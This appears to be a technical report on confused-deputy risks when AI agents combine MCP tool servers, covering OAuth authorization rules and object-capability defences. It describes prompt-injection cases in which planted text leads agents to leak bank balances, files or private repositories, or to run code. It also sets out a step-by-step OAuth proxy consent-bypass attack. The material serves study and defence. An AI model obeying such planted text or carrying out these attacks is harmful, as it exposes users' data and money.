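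The 27.2% figure shows that the parts of an attack are common. It includes any server with at least one tool that suits at least one stage, even if the tool has no fault. For example, 37% of the servers for communication and email had a tool that could send data out, which is a large part of why people install them. The figure doesn't show how many people have connected a set of servers that covers all three stages, because the researchers collected servers and not users' configurations.

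The count may also be too low. The researchers couldn't get the outside accounts that about 30% of the servers needed, for instance because signing up required a credit card. Those servers hold credentials, so the study probably missed many of the servers that matter most for confused-deputy attacks. It also covered only servers that users install and run themselves.

### Tests with honest servers

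To test whether the stages could be combined, the same researchers chose ten popular tools for each stage and built ten chains from them. Nine chains randomly combined tools from different servers, and the tenth used three tools from a single Microsoft 365 server. In each trial, a user of the code editor Cursor made a routine request that led the agent to read planted text. The trial succeeded if private data reached the destination the researchers had designated as the attacker's.

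*Parasites in the Toolchain* tested ten chains ten times each, and 36 of the 100 trials succeeded. The paper gives more prominence to its finding that nine of the ten chains worked, but it counts a chain as working if even one trial succeeded. The most successful chain ran from a web page to a local file to Gmail and worked eight times. The one that always failed required the model to collect data from a project-planning board and disclose it through a tool for organizing a record collection. The paper concludes that a model follows a chain more readily when the chain's tools are related.

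Nobody had tampered with the servers in these tests, and the agent used only permissions that the user had given it. But the researchers had set Cursor to run every call without asking for approval, so the results apply to people who work that way. According to Anthropic usage figures cited in the paper, about 20% of new users and over 40% of experienced ones approve everything automatically.

*MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* (Dhamsania, 2026) reports a higher success rate of 78.3% for attacks against an agent with five servers. It credits the figure to a research unit at Palo Alto Networks but links to a different company's blog. The article doesn't name the models or give the rate for an agent with one server, so the figure isn't evidence that adding servers made the attacks more successful.

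### When one of the servers is malicious

In *Trivial Trojans*, Croce and South (2025) tested what happens if a user installs a malicious server. They added fewer than 25 lines of code to the example weather server from MCP's documentation. One of them connected it to Claude Desktop, along with a server for his own account at Monzo, a British bank. When he asked for a forecast, Claude looked up his balance and passed it to a tool on the weather server. That tool sent the balance (£1,469.36), his location and the time to an outside web address.

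The weather server had no access to the bank and never received the Monzo token. The agent was authorized to read the balance, and text from the weather server led it to do so.

Croce and South report one demonstration and no success rate. Claude Desktop asked for approval before every call, including the one that sent the data out, and the person who approved the calls knew about the attack. An ordinary user might have questioned why a weather forecast required a bank balance. The instructions also arrived in a prompt template, a ready-made request that a server offers and the user chooses to run. A model has more reason to treat a template as the user's request than to treat a line in a stranger's email that way.

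A malicious server can also do damage without causing any extra calls. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of 38 threats to MCP systems, describes "cross-server tool shadowing", in which text from one server stays in the model's context and later changes how the agent uses another server's tool. In its example, a user asks the agent to email a confidential report, and text from a weather server leads the agent to add a hidden recipient. The user did want to send an email, and it looks ordinary in the logs. This resembles the wrong payment in the invoice example.

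The catalogue's summary table defines the same entry differently, as a malicious tool that replaces a trusted tool of the same name. A host could prevent this by refusing duplicate names, but that would do nothing about the hidden recipient.

Shen and colleagues included a threat only if someone had carried it out, in a laboratory or against a live system. An entry therefore shows that an attack is possible but not how often it works. They also don't always distinguish laboratory demonstrations from attacks in the field. For example, they describe the "GitHub MCP Data Heist" of 2025 as the work of attackers who stole private material, but it was a demonstration by security researchers.

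### Cases in released products

*GitHub MCP Exploited* (Invariant Labs, 2025) describes a demonstration in which a user with one public and one private repository had connected Claude Desktop to GitHub's official server. Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository. After reading an issue with planted text, the agent read the private repository and published data from it in a public pull request, a proposed code change that anyone can see.

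heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the attack needed no bug in the server, which works with the user's whole account. The outsider's text and the private data both came through that one server, so strictly speaking this was misuse across repositories and not across servers. Disconnecting the user's other servers would not have helped. According to DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP*, the researchers said that developers could avoid the problem by checking each action, but suspected that many choose "always allow".

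Herkos' *Exfil through an approved tool* found no official reply from GitHub to the disclosure. But in August 2025, GitHub (2025) announced that its server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets, and presented this as a protection against prompt injection. The scan could catch an access token on its way into a public pull request, but it would probably miss a confidential business plan, which looks like any other text.

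Cyata's *How We Found Code Execution in Anthropic’s Official Git MCP Server* describes a January 2026 case involving two of Anthropic's servers. The server for Git, a program that tracks versions of code, had a flaw that let an agent create a repository in any folder, even if the user had configured the server for only one. The Filesystem server let the agent write files. Someone who could plant text in the agent's context could use the two together to run commands on the user's computer, although neither server had a tool for running commands. Code editors that could write files themselves could replace the Filesystem server.

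Cyata first reported problems in June 2025, and Anthropic initially classed the report as informative. Anthropic reopened the case after a second report in July showed that an attacker could run code, and released a fix in December. Cyata also advised users to review which servers they combine, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Bugs Found in Official Anthropic Git MCP Server*. The fix repaired an ordinary programming mistake, and Cyata gives no figure for how often a model would make the necessary calls. Still, someone testing the Git server alone could easily have missed the worst consequence, because it depended on what another server could do.

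LayerX's *Claude Desktop Extensions Exposes Over 10,000 Users to Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* describes a user who asked Claude to check Google Calendar and "take care of it". One calendar entry contained instructions, and Claude followed them by running code through Desktop Commander, an extension with the user's full privileges on the computer. Because Claude could both read the calendar and run programs, whoever wrote the entry could control the computer.

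Anthropic declined to change anything and said the attack was outside its threat model, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Flaw in Claude Desktop Extensions, Anthropic Declines Fix*. A spokesperson pointed out that the user must have installed both tools and allowed them to run without prompts. This description is fair, and it makes LayerX's maximum severity score for the flaw look too high. LayerX's figure of 10,000 affected users seems to count everyone with the extensions, not only those who had connected both a calendar and a program that runs code. LayerX calls the attack reliable but doesn't give the model version or the number of trials.

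But Anthropic's answer assumes that people who approve two tools have also approved what the tools can do together. Someone might reasonably trust a calendar reader and a code runner separately and never consider that, with both connected, a meeting invitation could start a program.

A researcher at the security company Radware found a related attack on ChatGPT, in which planted instructions could make it leak data from connected services such as Gmail, Google Drive and GitHub. He reported it in September 2025 and OpenAI fixed the flaw in mid-December, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

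### Harm to real users

All these product cases came from researchers. Aviatrix, a security company, reports no confirmed exploitation of the Git server's flaws. After the GitHub demonstration, Maple wrote in *The Dark Side of “Just Hooking Up” AI Agents to GitHub* that there was no known active attack of that kind.

Criminals have done damage through tool servers in other ways. Mittwald, a German web host, ran an MCP server that let customers' AI assistants manage their hosting accounts. Marc David (2026), in *MCP Security Best Practices After the Mittwald Breach*, reports that a flaw in this server exposed users' session tokens to an attacker, who then broke into 56 of the customers' projects. The attacker stole credentials and did not need to mislead anyone's agent. The Instagram thefts of 2026 are closer to the confused-deputy problem because Meta's assistant used its authority for people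 who lacked it, but they did not depend on text from one server affecting another.

The lack of known victims might mean that criminals have easier methods, or that victims don't notice. An agent that leaks a file makes calls with valid credentials, using tools the user approved, so the logs may look like normal use. The available reports don't show which explanation matters more.

### What carries over to newer models

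*Parasites in the Toolchain* also compares models. The researchers ran the chain from web page to local file to Gmail in five host programs, with three versions of the planted text and five attempts at each. They again turned off approval prompts. Adding up their results gives these totals:

| Model | Attempts that leaked the file | Share |
| --- | --- | --- |
| DeepSeek R1 | 45 of 60 | 75% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 53 of 75 | 71% |
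| Cursor's default setting | 9 of 15 | 60% |
| GPT-4.1 | 12 of 75 | 16% |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 11 of 75 | 15% |
| GPT-5 | 0 of 75 | 0% |
| Claude 4.5 Sonnet | 0 of 75 | 0% |

GPT-5 and Claude 4.5 Sonnet are both more than a year old as of December 2026, and the leading models that followed them would probably resist these texts too. The 36 successes in 100 trials with Cursor's default setting therefore poorly estimate the risk to someone using a leading model in late 2026. They may be a better guide for people who still run older or cheaper models.

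An attack could still work even though none of the 75 attempts did. If each attempt independently had a 4% chance of success, all 75 would still fail about 5% of the time (0.96^75 ≈ 0.05). The attempts were not actually independent, since they shared three texts. The researchers also didn't report rewriting the texts that failed, as a real attacker would. The table shows that the better models resisted three particular attacks, but it doesn't show how they would do against someone who kept trying.

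The host program can also affect how often a model leaks data. The researchers found that every model except GPT-4.1 behaved similarly in all the hosts. GPT-4.1 leaked the file in 9 of 15 attempts in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, but in only 3 of 60 in the other hosts. A model's good result in one product may not hold in another with different instructions and tools.

The number of exploitable tools doesn't depend on the model, because a tool that sends email can send a stolen file whichever model calls it. Some software flaws don't depend on the model's judgement either. In July 2026, Manifold Security showed that any other browser extension could make Claude for Chrome read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Calendar. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, explains that the extension started one of nine built-in tasks when it detected a click, without checking that a person had clicked.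 No tool servers were involved, but this is a confused deputy much like Hardy's compiler. A more careful model would not solve the problem, because the software presents the forged click as a real request from the user.

Products can also mix up connections without an attacker. In *Security*, a November post on OpenAI's developer forum, AldiPower (2026) describes a conversation in which ChatGPT had two connectors. It received a one-time confirmation code through the first and sent it through the second without telling the user. Both connectors led to the same server, so no outsider obtained the code. If the connectors had belonged to different companies, the same mistake could have given one company a code meant for the other.

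## What OAuth and the Model Context Protocol already prevent

OAuth and the Model Context Protocol (MCP) have rules that keep several kinds of program from becoming confused deputies, but few of these rules protect the agent. Under the heading "Confused Deputy Problem", MCP's *Security Best Practices* describes an attack that misleads a server and involves no language model.

### A proxy that gives away a user's access

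Some MCP servers are proxies for another company's service, such as a cloud drive. In OAuth, such a proxy issues tokens to the applications that connect to it and is itself an application that needs a token from the drive. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* found this arrangement in 81 of the 119 servers that its researchers tested closely.

The attack depends on how OAuth delivers tokens. When a user grants an application access, the authorization server sends the user's browser, with a short-lived authorization code, to a redirect address that the application registered earlier. The application then exchanges the code for a token. If the code goes to the wrong address, someone else may get that access.

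The proxy is vulnerable if four things are true. It uses one fixed client ID (the name by which an authorization server knows an application) at the drive, whichever application it is working for. It lets any application register with it automatically. The drive remembers a user's consent in a browser cookie. And the proxy doesn't ask the user to approve each new application. The attack then goes like this:

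1. The user connects an honest application through the proxy. The drive asks for consent, the user agrees, and the drive sets a cookie recording that this user approved the proxy's client ID.
2. The attacker registers an application with the proxy and gives an address on the attacker's own site as its redirect address.
3. The attacker sends the user a link that starts an authorization for this new application, and the user clicks it.
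4. The browser reaches the drive with the proxy's usual client ID. The drive finds the cookie, skips the consent screen and sends the proxy a code.
5. The proxy exchanges that code for access to the drive. It then creates a code of its own for the new application and sends the browser to the attacker's address with it.
6. The attacker exchanges the second code for a token and uses the victim's drive through the proxy.

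The proxy is the deputy here, since it can reach the user's files and the attacker can't. As at Tymshare, the destination and the permission came from different parties. The attacker chose the redirect address, and the user had earlier consented to the proxy's access to the drive. The drive can't distinguish the attacker's request from the user's because both carry the same client ID.

To prevent this, the proxy must get the user's consent itself before it sends the browser to the drive. It keeps a list of the applications each user has approved. The attacker's application isn't on the list, so the proxy shows a page with the application's name, the access it requests and the address that will receive the code, and continues only if the user approves. The proxy must also check that the redirect address exactly matches the registered one. It must not set the cookie that tracks the sign-in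 until the user has approved, because otherwise a crafted request could bypass the page.

A user might still approve an application that calls itself "Claude", which is why the consent page has to show the redirect address. The measurement study found servers that left the address out. It also found at least one flaw in all 119 servers, and flaws in automatic registration in 96.6% of them. The researchers tested only servers that offer automatic registration, so these figures may not apply to other servers. One of the flaws they counted was accepting any redirect address from an unknown application, which is close to what open registration is for. It becomes dangerous when the user never sees a proper consent page. The researchers also did not take real users' data, so the study doesn't show how many servers the full attack would have worked on.

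### Tokens that work at only one server

In token passthrough, a server accepts a token without checking that it was the intended recipient, then forwards the token unchanged. Suppose the payment server in the invoice example forwarded the token it received from the agent's host to the bank in this way. The bank might assume that the payment server had already checked the request, and the bank's logs might show the wrong source. A thief with a stolen token could also use the payment server as a relay.

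The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) forbids a server from forwarding its client's token to another service. The server must instead use a separate token issued by that service's own authorization server. This rule protects the service being called, such as a bank, from becoming a confused deputy.

A server can reject tokens meant for other servers only if each token shows where it is valid. RFC 8707, an extension to OAuth, does this with "resource indicators". The client includes the tool server's address in a `resource` parameter when it asks for the user's authorization and again when it requests the token. The authorization server then binds the token to that address as its audience.

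Audience checks protect the payment server from the mail server. If both trust the same company login system and neither checks audiences, a malicious mail server could take the token it receives from the host and present it to the payment server, which would then make payments in the user's name. Dissanayaka calls this kind of audience confusion the most common exploit in production, but gives no figures.

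The protection needs three parties to cooperate. An MCP client must send the `resource` parameter even if the authorization server ignores it, but according to Model Context Protocol, tokens are bound to an audience only if the authorization server supports that binding.

The host's own client can be a deputy too, because it deals with many authorization servers and one of them may be malicious. In a "mix-up" attack, the malicious server gets the client to send it a code that an honest authorization server issued. OAuth's usual protection for codes, PKCE, makes the client prove with a secret that it started the authorization. This doesn't help here because the client sends the attacker the secret along with the code. Audience binding doesn't help either if the attacker intercepts the request before it reaches the honest server.

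To defend against the attack, the client records which authorization server it is sending the user to, then compares that with the `iss` ("issuer") field in the reply. According to Model Context Protocol (2026), the check adds little overhead, and the attack is more common where one client connects to many servers. But authorization servers "should" include the field and are not required to. If an honest server omits it and has never advertised support for it, the client proceeds without this protection.

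### Carrying the user's identity to the next service

Once passthrough is forbidden, the payment server needs another credential for the bank. If it uses a service account, it has to enforce every customer's limits itself. RFC 8693 defines an alternative, token exchange, in which the payment server presents the user's token to an authorization server and receives a new one for the bank. The new token can identify the user and, in a field called `act`, the program acting for that user.

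The bank can then apply the user's own limits. This keeps a server with broad authority from using it on behalf of people who have less, such as the employee in the earlier example who asks an agent for everyone's salaries.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) does not base its authorization rules on RFC 8693, the OAuth standard for token exchange. *OAuth in MCP* (tianpan.co, 2026) points to an open request for token exchange in MCP's public repository and describes current company integrations as improvised.

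An optional MCP extension does use token exchange, but at a different point. SlashID's *Breaking MCP at the Identity Layer* explains that Enterprise-Managed Authorization, which became stable in June 2026, moves the decision to grant access from the employee to the company's login system. The host's client presents proof that the employee has logged in. The login system checks company policy and returns a signed statement valid for 300 seconds, which the client exchanges for an access token to one MCP server. The employee sees no consent screen that an attacker could use to trick them.

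The access token can last much longer than the statement behind it. The token in the extension's example lasts 24 hours, so an employee may keep access for most of a day after an administrator withdraws it. The exchange also covers only one hop. If one agent hands work to a second, the final token may identify the user but not the first agent or the text that influenced that agent. SlashID has a reason to stress these gaps because it sells software to monitor them, but anyone can check the token lifetimes.

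### How the rules changed between 2024 and 2026

MCP acquired these protections over five releases:

- The November 2024 release had no mandatory authentication for remote servers.
- In March 2025, Model Context Protocol (2025) added its first authorization framework, based on OAuth 2.1.
- In June 2025, Model Context Protocol classed tool servers as OAuth resource servers, meaning that they check tokens and need not issue them. It also required clients to use resource indicators, to keep malicious servers from obtaining usable tokens. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* (2025), first published with this release, treats token passthrough as forbidden.
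- In November 2025, Model Context Protocol let servers ask for further scopes when a call needs them. It also recommended a new way for applications to identify themselves, in which an application's client ID is a web address containing a description of it.
- In July 2026, Model Context Protocol required clients to check `iss` when it is present and to keep each set of client credentials with the authorization server that issued it. It also deprecated automatic registration, which will remain available for at least twelve months.

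A proxy that stops offering automatic registration no longer meets one of the four conditions the guidance lists for the attack. But an attacker can also publish an application's description at a web address, so a proxy that accepts unknown applications still has to ask the user to approve each one. The wording of the July 2026 specification doesn't fully reflect this. It requires a proxy with a fixed client ID to get consent for each "dynamically registered" client, while the accompanying guidance requires consent for every client.

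*Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) describes the July changes as clarifications of established OAuth practice that introduce no fundamentally new concepts. That seems right, and it is a reason to trust the changes, since other systems have used these mechanisms for years. It also means the changes rely on OAuth's assumption that an application with a valid token is doing what its user wants.

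Authorization is optional in MCP, which recommends but does not require that servers using it over the web follow these rules. *Exposed by Design* found that some servers' checks were ineffective because they used fixed tokens that were predictable or even blank.

### Servers that cannot tell callers apart

A server can hold a properly issued token for an outside service and still let the wrong program use it. Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*, call this caller identity confusion. After a user authorizes the server once, the server remembers this and accepts calls from any program that can reach it. Some servers for the messaging service Slack, for example, log in with a powerful token when they start. Anyone who can call their tools can then read or post messages without a Slack credential.

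Huang and colleagues looked for the problem in 6,137 server projects written in Python or JavaScript. Their software located each server's tools in the source code and traced whether a call could reach a sensitive operation, such as running a command, without a check on that call. If this was unclear from the code, the software ran the server and tried the call. The team rated 2,846 servers (46.4%) insecure.

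That figure covers more than caller confusion. Adding up the paper's categories gives 1,279 insecure servers with no authorization check, which is a simpler fault than failing to track who obtained an authorization. The same breakdown rates only 2,554 servers as secure, which leaves 737 unrated. Of the rated servers, 52.7% are insecure.

The study measures flawed code, which doesn't always leave a server open to attack. Many of these projects run on a user's own computer and communicate only with the host that started them, so a stranger can't call them unless someone puts them on a network. The researchers tested servers only in their own test environment, not in real use. Still, they also examined 87 popular projects and found 8 with authentication problems that could let an attacker run commands remotely.

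Huang and colleagues propose tying each authorization to a session that begins with the opening handshake of the Model Context Protocol (MCP). MCP's July 2026 release removed both, so servers now have to identify the caller on every request. MCP's guidance is that servers should store any data under a user ID taken from the verified token, so another caller can't use the data by guessing its label.

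A server that does all this knows which user's agent is calling. In the invoice attacks, it is the right user's agent.

### A valid token on every call

Suppose the invoice agent's servers follow every rule so far. The mail server receives only a mail token. If it turns malicious and sends that token to the payment server, the audience check fails. But the agent's host has a token for each server and attaches the right one to any call the model proposes. The payment server's checks then give these results:

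| Payment server's check | Mail server presents its mail token | Agent pays the supplier | Agent pays the attacker |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Is the token genuine and unexpired? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Does it come from a trusted authorization server? | Yes, if both servers use the same one | Yes | Yes |
| Is this server its audience? | No | Yes | Yes |
| Does its scope allow creating payments? | Not reached | Yes | Yes |
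| Result | Refused | Paid | Paid |

The last two columns are identical because every check concerns the token, and the token is the same in both cases. Only the account number in the call's arguments differs. The theft of the contracts works the same way. The host sends the file token to the file server and the mail token to the mail server, and each server accepts the token it receives.

Audience binding separates the servers from one another, but the agent still holds credentials for all of them. Dissanayaka regards the July 2026 release as a serious tightening of security, but notes that OAuth records the user's consent once and the agent may act on it hundreds of calls later in ways the user never imagined. Dissanayaka leaves it to the software around the agent to check whether an action is still what the user wanted.

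### How much scopes can narrow

Of these rules, only scopes reduce what the agent itself can do. The Model Context Protocol recommends starting with a few scopes that cover only low-risk operations, such as reading. If the agent later attempts an operation they don't cover, the server rejects the request and returns the required scope. The client then requests a new token with that scope, usually with the user's consent, and tries again.

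This could expose the theft to an attentive user. If the agent had no permission to read files, the planted request for the contracts would bring up a consent screen about file access while the user was waiting for a bill to be paid.

Several details of the rules make that less likely. A client should add the scopes it now needs to the ones it had before, so that other operations keep their permissions. The agent's authority therefore tends to grow, and an attack that needs file access may not bring up a consent screen if the user approved that access for a different job last week. The guidance also recommends that servers request related scopes together to reduce interruptions. If a server doesn't name the scopes it needs at the start, the client requests every scope on the server's published list. That list is supposed to be minimal, but the guidance names publishing every possible scope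 as a common mistake.

These choices make more sense given that the guidance is meant to address stolen tokens. A narrower token limits what a thief can do. An agent under an attacker's influence is a different problem because it can request more authority from a user who is used to saying yes. A host could instead derive new scopes from each task, but MCP has no rule for doing so.

Even the narrowest useful scope doesn't prevent the wrong payment, because a scope such as `payments:create` specifies a kind of operation, not a payee. The Model Context Protocol lets a server consider a call's arguments when deciding which scopes to require, so a payment server could define a separate scope for each payee. But scopes are short text labels, which makes them a clumsy way to express an amount, a currency and an account number.

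### Naming one payment in the authorization request

RFC 9396, an OAuth extension called Rich Authorization Requests, exists for cases like this. It lets a client send structured details in a field called `authorization_details`, alongside scopes or in place of them. Each entry must have a type, and the designers of a service decide what else that type contains. For the invoice, an entry could look like this:

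```json
{
  "type": "payment_initiation",
  "instructedAmount": { "currency": "GBP", "amount": "480.00" },
  "creditorName": "Northgate Paper",
  "creditorAccount": { "iban": "the supplier's account number" }
}
```

The authorization server shows the user these details and, if the user approves, issues a token for that payment. When the agent makes the call, the payment server compares the arguments with the approved details and rejects the call if the amount or account differs. It must also refuse to make the same approved payment twice, since a token can normally be reused until it expires.

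How much this helps depends on where the account number came from. If the host takes it from the user's saved payees, an account number in the email has no effect. If the model copies it from the email, the request contains the attacker's account number from the start. The user then sees the expected supplier and amount next to an account number that few people know by heart. If the user approves, the token authorizes that payment to the attacker.

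The approval page is still an improvement. The authorization server produces it, so the model can't describe one payment to the user and request another. Once the user has approved the correct details, nothing the agent reads afterwards can redirect the money. However, the user has to approve every payment, and people who approve many requests tend to stop reading them.

In the case of the stolen contracts, the file server would have to define an authorization type that limits access to particular folders, and the mail server one that limits recipients. RFC 9396 supplies the format but leaves these definitions to each service. MCP's list of standards does not include RFC 9396. When an MCP server refuses a call for lack of permission, its reply has a standard field for the missing scopes but none for limits such as folders or recipients. A host and a payment service could agree on their own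 format, but a general-purpose client connecting to a new server has no standard way to determine which limits to request.

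## Object capabilities as references in place of standing access

A token issued under Rich Authorization Requests can describe a single payment, but the agent still sends an account number with its call, and the payment server has to compare that number with the token. In an object-capability system, the agent holds a reference to one payee, and calls made through it have no account number field, so the server has nothing to compare. An agent without such a reference can't pay anyone.

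### Four ways to obtain a reference

In this model, an object is a piece of running software with private data of its own. It can be as large as a payment server or as small as ten lines of code in front of one. Objects affect each other only by sending messages, and an object can send a message only to something it has a reference to. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, lists all the ways to get a reference. For an agent and a folder, they are:

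- Initial conditions: the agent already had the reference when the system started.
- Creation: the agent creates the folder, and at first it has the only reference to it.
- Endowment: the host has a reference to the folder and creates the agent with a copy of it.
- Introduction: the host has references to both the agent and the folder, and sends the agent a message that includes its reference to the folder.

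Knowing a folder's name doesn't give an agent a reference to it. A stranger's email can tell the agent that a contracts folder exists and even give its full path, but the sender can't pass on a reference to the folder without already having one. Miller sums this up as "only connectivity begets connectivity". This rule lets someone work out the worst case by mapping who has references to what. Nothing the model writes can move money if no path leads from the agent to the bank, and if there is a path, the outcome depends on how the programs along it behave.

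A capability, in this sense, is a reference of this kind. The word has several other meanings that turn up in writing about agents:

- AI developers use it for a model's skills, such as writing code.
- In MCP, capabilities are optional features that a client or server supports. A server that declares the `tools` capability has not given anyone permission to do anything.
- In the POSIX standard for operating systems, a capability is a flag that confers a broad power. Miller and colleagues give the example of `CAP_CHOWN`, which lets a program change the owner of any file on the machine.
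- In *AgentCap* (2026), a capability is a permit for a tool call. A gate outside the model issues it, and a gateway checks it before forwarding the call. It works only within one session and one line of agents. The paper acknowledges that narrow permits are not enough if an attacker manipulates the arguments of a legitimate operation, as in the wrong payment.

### Passing names and passing open files

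Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, compare two Unix commands that both copy a file:

```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The `cp` program receives two file names and opens the files itself. Since the user might type any name, `cp` needs permission to open every file the user can open. In the `cat` command, the shell (the program that interprets what the user types) opens both files and passes them to `cat`. The `cat` program needs only those two open files, although Unix still lets it use the rest of the user's permissions.

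Like `cp`, an agent connected through MCP refers to resources by name. Its tool calls contain names such as a folder path or an account number, so its credentials have to cover any resource the user might mean.

Miller and colleagues break the difference between the two styles down into seven properties. Five of them matter most here. Object-capability systems have all five, and the Unix and Windows NT file permissions that the paper examines have none:

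| Property | Meaning | Effect on the invoice agent |
| --- | --- | --- |
| No designation without authority | Pointing to a resource always supplies the permission to use it | An account number in an email is only text, and the agent can't pay it |
| No ambient authority | A program has to select the permission it uses | The agent can't pay just because a login happens to be active |
| Dynamic subject creation | A running program can create new holders of permissions | Each task can have its own agent with its own references |
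| Composability of authorities | A program can stand in for a resource | The host can put a restricted version of the payment server in front of the real one |
| Access-controlled delegation channels | Passing a reference to someone requires a reference to them | An agent with no outgoing channel can't pass its references to an attacker |

A system has no designation without authority if every reference to a resource carries permission to use it. Such a system also has no ambient authority. Every request has to refer to a resource, so the requester chooses which permission to use by choosing a reference, whereas Hardy's compiler had no way to choose which of its permissions a request would use.

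### The comparison with access lists

Many researchers have believed that capabilities and access lists are formally equivalent. The argument starts from a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each resource, where each cell shows what that user or program may do to that resource. An access list is one column, stored with the resource, and a capability list is one row, stored with the program. Taken together, the columns seem to contain the same information as the rows.

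Miller and colleagues reply that the table shows permissions only at one moment. It leaves out how programs refer to resources and how the permissions change. Access lists need a separate system for naming resources, and this weakness led to Hardy's accident. A program that holds a list of references can use one directly, without a separate name.

Access lists also have to name whoever may use the resource, and they are hard to keep up to date if the names change often. They therefore usually name people or accounts rather than individual running programs. A company's file server may list an employee, but it probably won't list an agent the employee started just to pay one bill.

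Only the point about separate names applies to every possible access list. The paper presents the limit on individual programs as a fact about existing systems, and someone could build an access-list system that creates a new account for each run of an agent. Programs using that system would still have to name the file or payee they wanted.

Contrary to another common belief, whoever grants access through a capability can arrange to revoke that access later. Nobody else can remove a reference once a program holds it, but the grantor can hand out a reference to an intermediary that they can disable.

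### Wrappers, forwarders and membranes

A plain reference gives its holder full access for as long as the resource exists. To grant less, a program creates a new object that keeps the full reference private, then hands out a reference to that object.

An attenuating wrapper passes on only some requests. This one, in JavaScript, turns a reference to a whole payment server into permission to make one payment to one account:

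```js
function onePayment(payments, account, limit) {
  let used = false;
  return {
    pay(amount) {
      if (used || !(amount > 0 && amount <= limit)) throw "refused";
      used = true;
      return payments.create(account, amount);
    }
  };
}
```

The host calls `onePayment` with its full reference, the supplier's saved account and a limit, and gives the agent the result. The agent can call `pay` with an amount, but it can't reach `payments` or change `account`, because those variables are private to the function. Programmers can also nest wrappers. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) describes narrowing access from a whole file system to one file, and then to read-only access to that file.

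A revocable forwarder passes on every request until someone switches it off. The host creates two linked objects, a forwarder and a switch. It gives the agent the forwarder, which passes messages to, say, an invoices folder, and keeps the switch. Using the switch makes the forwarder drop its reference to the folder. The agent still has its reference to the forwarder but can no longer use it to reach the folder. If the agent has shared that reference with another agent, that agent loses access too. According to Miller and colleagues, Redell described this method in 1974, 27 years before one of the papers they criticize called revocation infeasible.

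Forwarders complicate audits. Miller points out that a list of everyone with permission to use the folder would not include the agent, because the agent has permission to use only the forwarder. An auditor would have to examine what the programs between the agent and the folder do.

A forwarder can also leak direct references. Suppose the agent uses it to open a file in the folder, and the folder returns a direct reference to that file. Switching off the forwarder then ends the agent's access to the folder but not to the file. A membrane prevents this by putting a forwarder around every reference that crosses it in either direction, with one switch for all of them. Plain data crosses without a wrapper because nobody can revoke it once it has been read. This is a large exception for a language model, because switching off the membrane doesn't remove the text of a contract that is already in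 the model's context.

### The powerbox

Someone still has to decide which references a program gets. With a powerbox, the user makes that decision while telling the program what to work on.

Habitat Chronicles explains the idea with Microsoft Word. When a user picks a document in the Open File dialog, the operating system gives Word the file's name, and Word opens the file with the user's permissions, which would also let it open any of the user's other files. In the capability version, the user sees the same dialog, but the operating system opens the file and hands it to Word. Word starts with no access, so the chosen file is the only one it can damage.

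Miller describes an experimental desktop, CapDesk, that worked this way for programs written in E, a capability language he helped develop. A companion system, Polaris, did the same for ordinary programs such as Excel. It ran each program in a separate account with very few permissions and gave that account access to a file when the user opened it. Miller reports that Polaris users regularly left spreadsheet macros switched on because they no longer feared their documents, but he gives no figures.

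Google Drive can similarly limit an app to the files that a user selects in Google's file picker. capOS's *Proposal*, a set of design notes for a small operating system, compares this to a powerbox but notes that each selection expands an access list.

### Paying the invoice with references

Suppose the host keeps the full references to the mail, file and payment servers and starts the agent with only a way to reach the user. The user has a £480 bill from Northgate Paper, a supplier they have paid before.

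| Step | References the agent holds afterwards |
| --- | --- |
| The host starts the agent with the user's request | `user`: send the user messages and ask for references |
| The agent asks for the invoice, and the user picks the email in a window drawn by the host | `user`; `invoice`: read that one message |
| The agent reads the email, including the planted text | `user`; `invoice` |
| The agent asks for a way to pay, and the user picks Northgate Paper from the saved payees and sets a limit of £500 | `user`; `invoice`; `payNorthgate`: make one payment of up to £500 to the saved account |
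| The agent calls `pay(480)` | `user`; `invoice`; `payNorthgate`, which no longer works |
| The task ends and the host switches everything off | None that work |

The agent can't steal the contracts with these references. It can't open the contracts folder, and even if it had the documents, it couldn't email them to anyone. Reading the planted text doesn't give it any new references.

The model also cannot send the payment to the wrong account, because `pay` accepts only an amount. The email may mislead the model into treating new bank details as the supplier's, but none of the model's available calls accept bank details.

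Planted text could still make the agent pay £500 instead of £480, or ask the user for the contracts folder and give a plausible reason. The protection also depends on Northgate Paper being a saved payee, because a new supplier's account number would probably come from the email.

The host needs careful protection in this design because it holds all the full references and draws the window where the user makes choices. Miller accepts the same risk in CapDesk, which needed all of its user's authority so it could give parts of it to other programs.

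### A demonstration with files

Endo is an open-source project for running JavaScript under object-capability rules. In 2026 it produced a prototype agent called Endo Familiar. The agent starts with one document it can read. The user then gives it a directory, and after that a read-only view, which is an attenuating wrapper.

*Create Endo AI Agent Capp*, a plan by kriskowal, describes in more detail how an Endo agent could work. The agent can store references under names of its own, exchange messages with the user, and ask for further capabilities. It has to request even its connection to the language model. When the model writes code, the agent turns it into a request to run the code, and the user sees that request.

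The Endo Familiar demonstration shows that an agent can receive its access one reference at a time. But it involves handing over only a few files, so it gives little evidence of how people would manage an agent that handled their mail, files and payments every day.

### A proposal for requests between agents

Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) proposes adding capability requests to A2A, a protocol for communication between agents. Semgrep, a software security company, published the idea in January 2026 and opened a discussion with the A2A project. It is a proposal, with message formats but no test results. A task would go as follows:

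1. A server publishes the kinds of access it can grant, such as reading files.
2. Before using any tools, the agent requests access for its task. It gives a purpose, such as summarizing quarterly reports, and sets limits: one folder, reading and listing only, and an expiry time.
3. The server issues a capability for whatever the published grant, the request and its own policy all allow.
4. The agent includes the capability's ID in each tool call, and the server rejects any call that the capability doesn't cover.
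5. If the agent passes work to another agent, it first derives a narrower capability, for example for one report in the folder.

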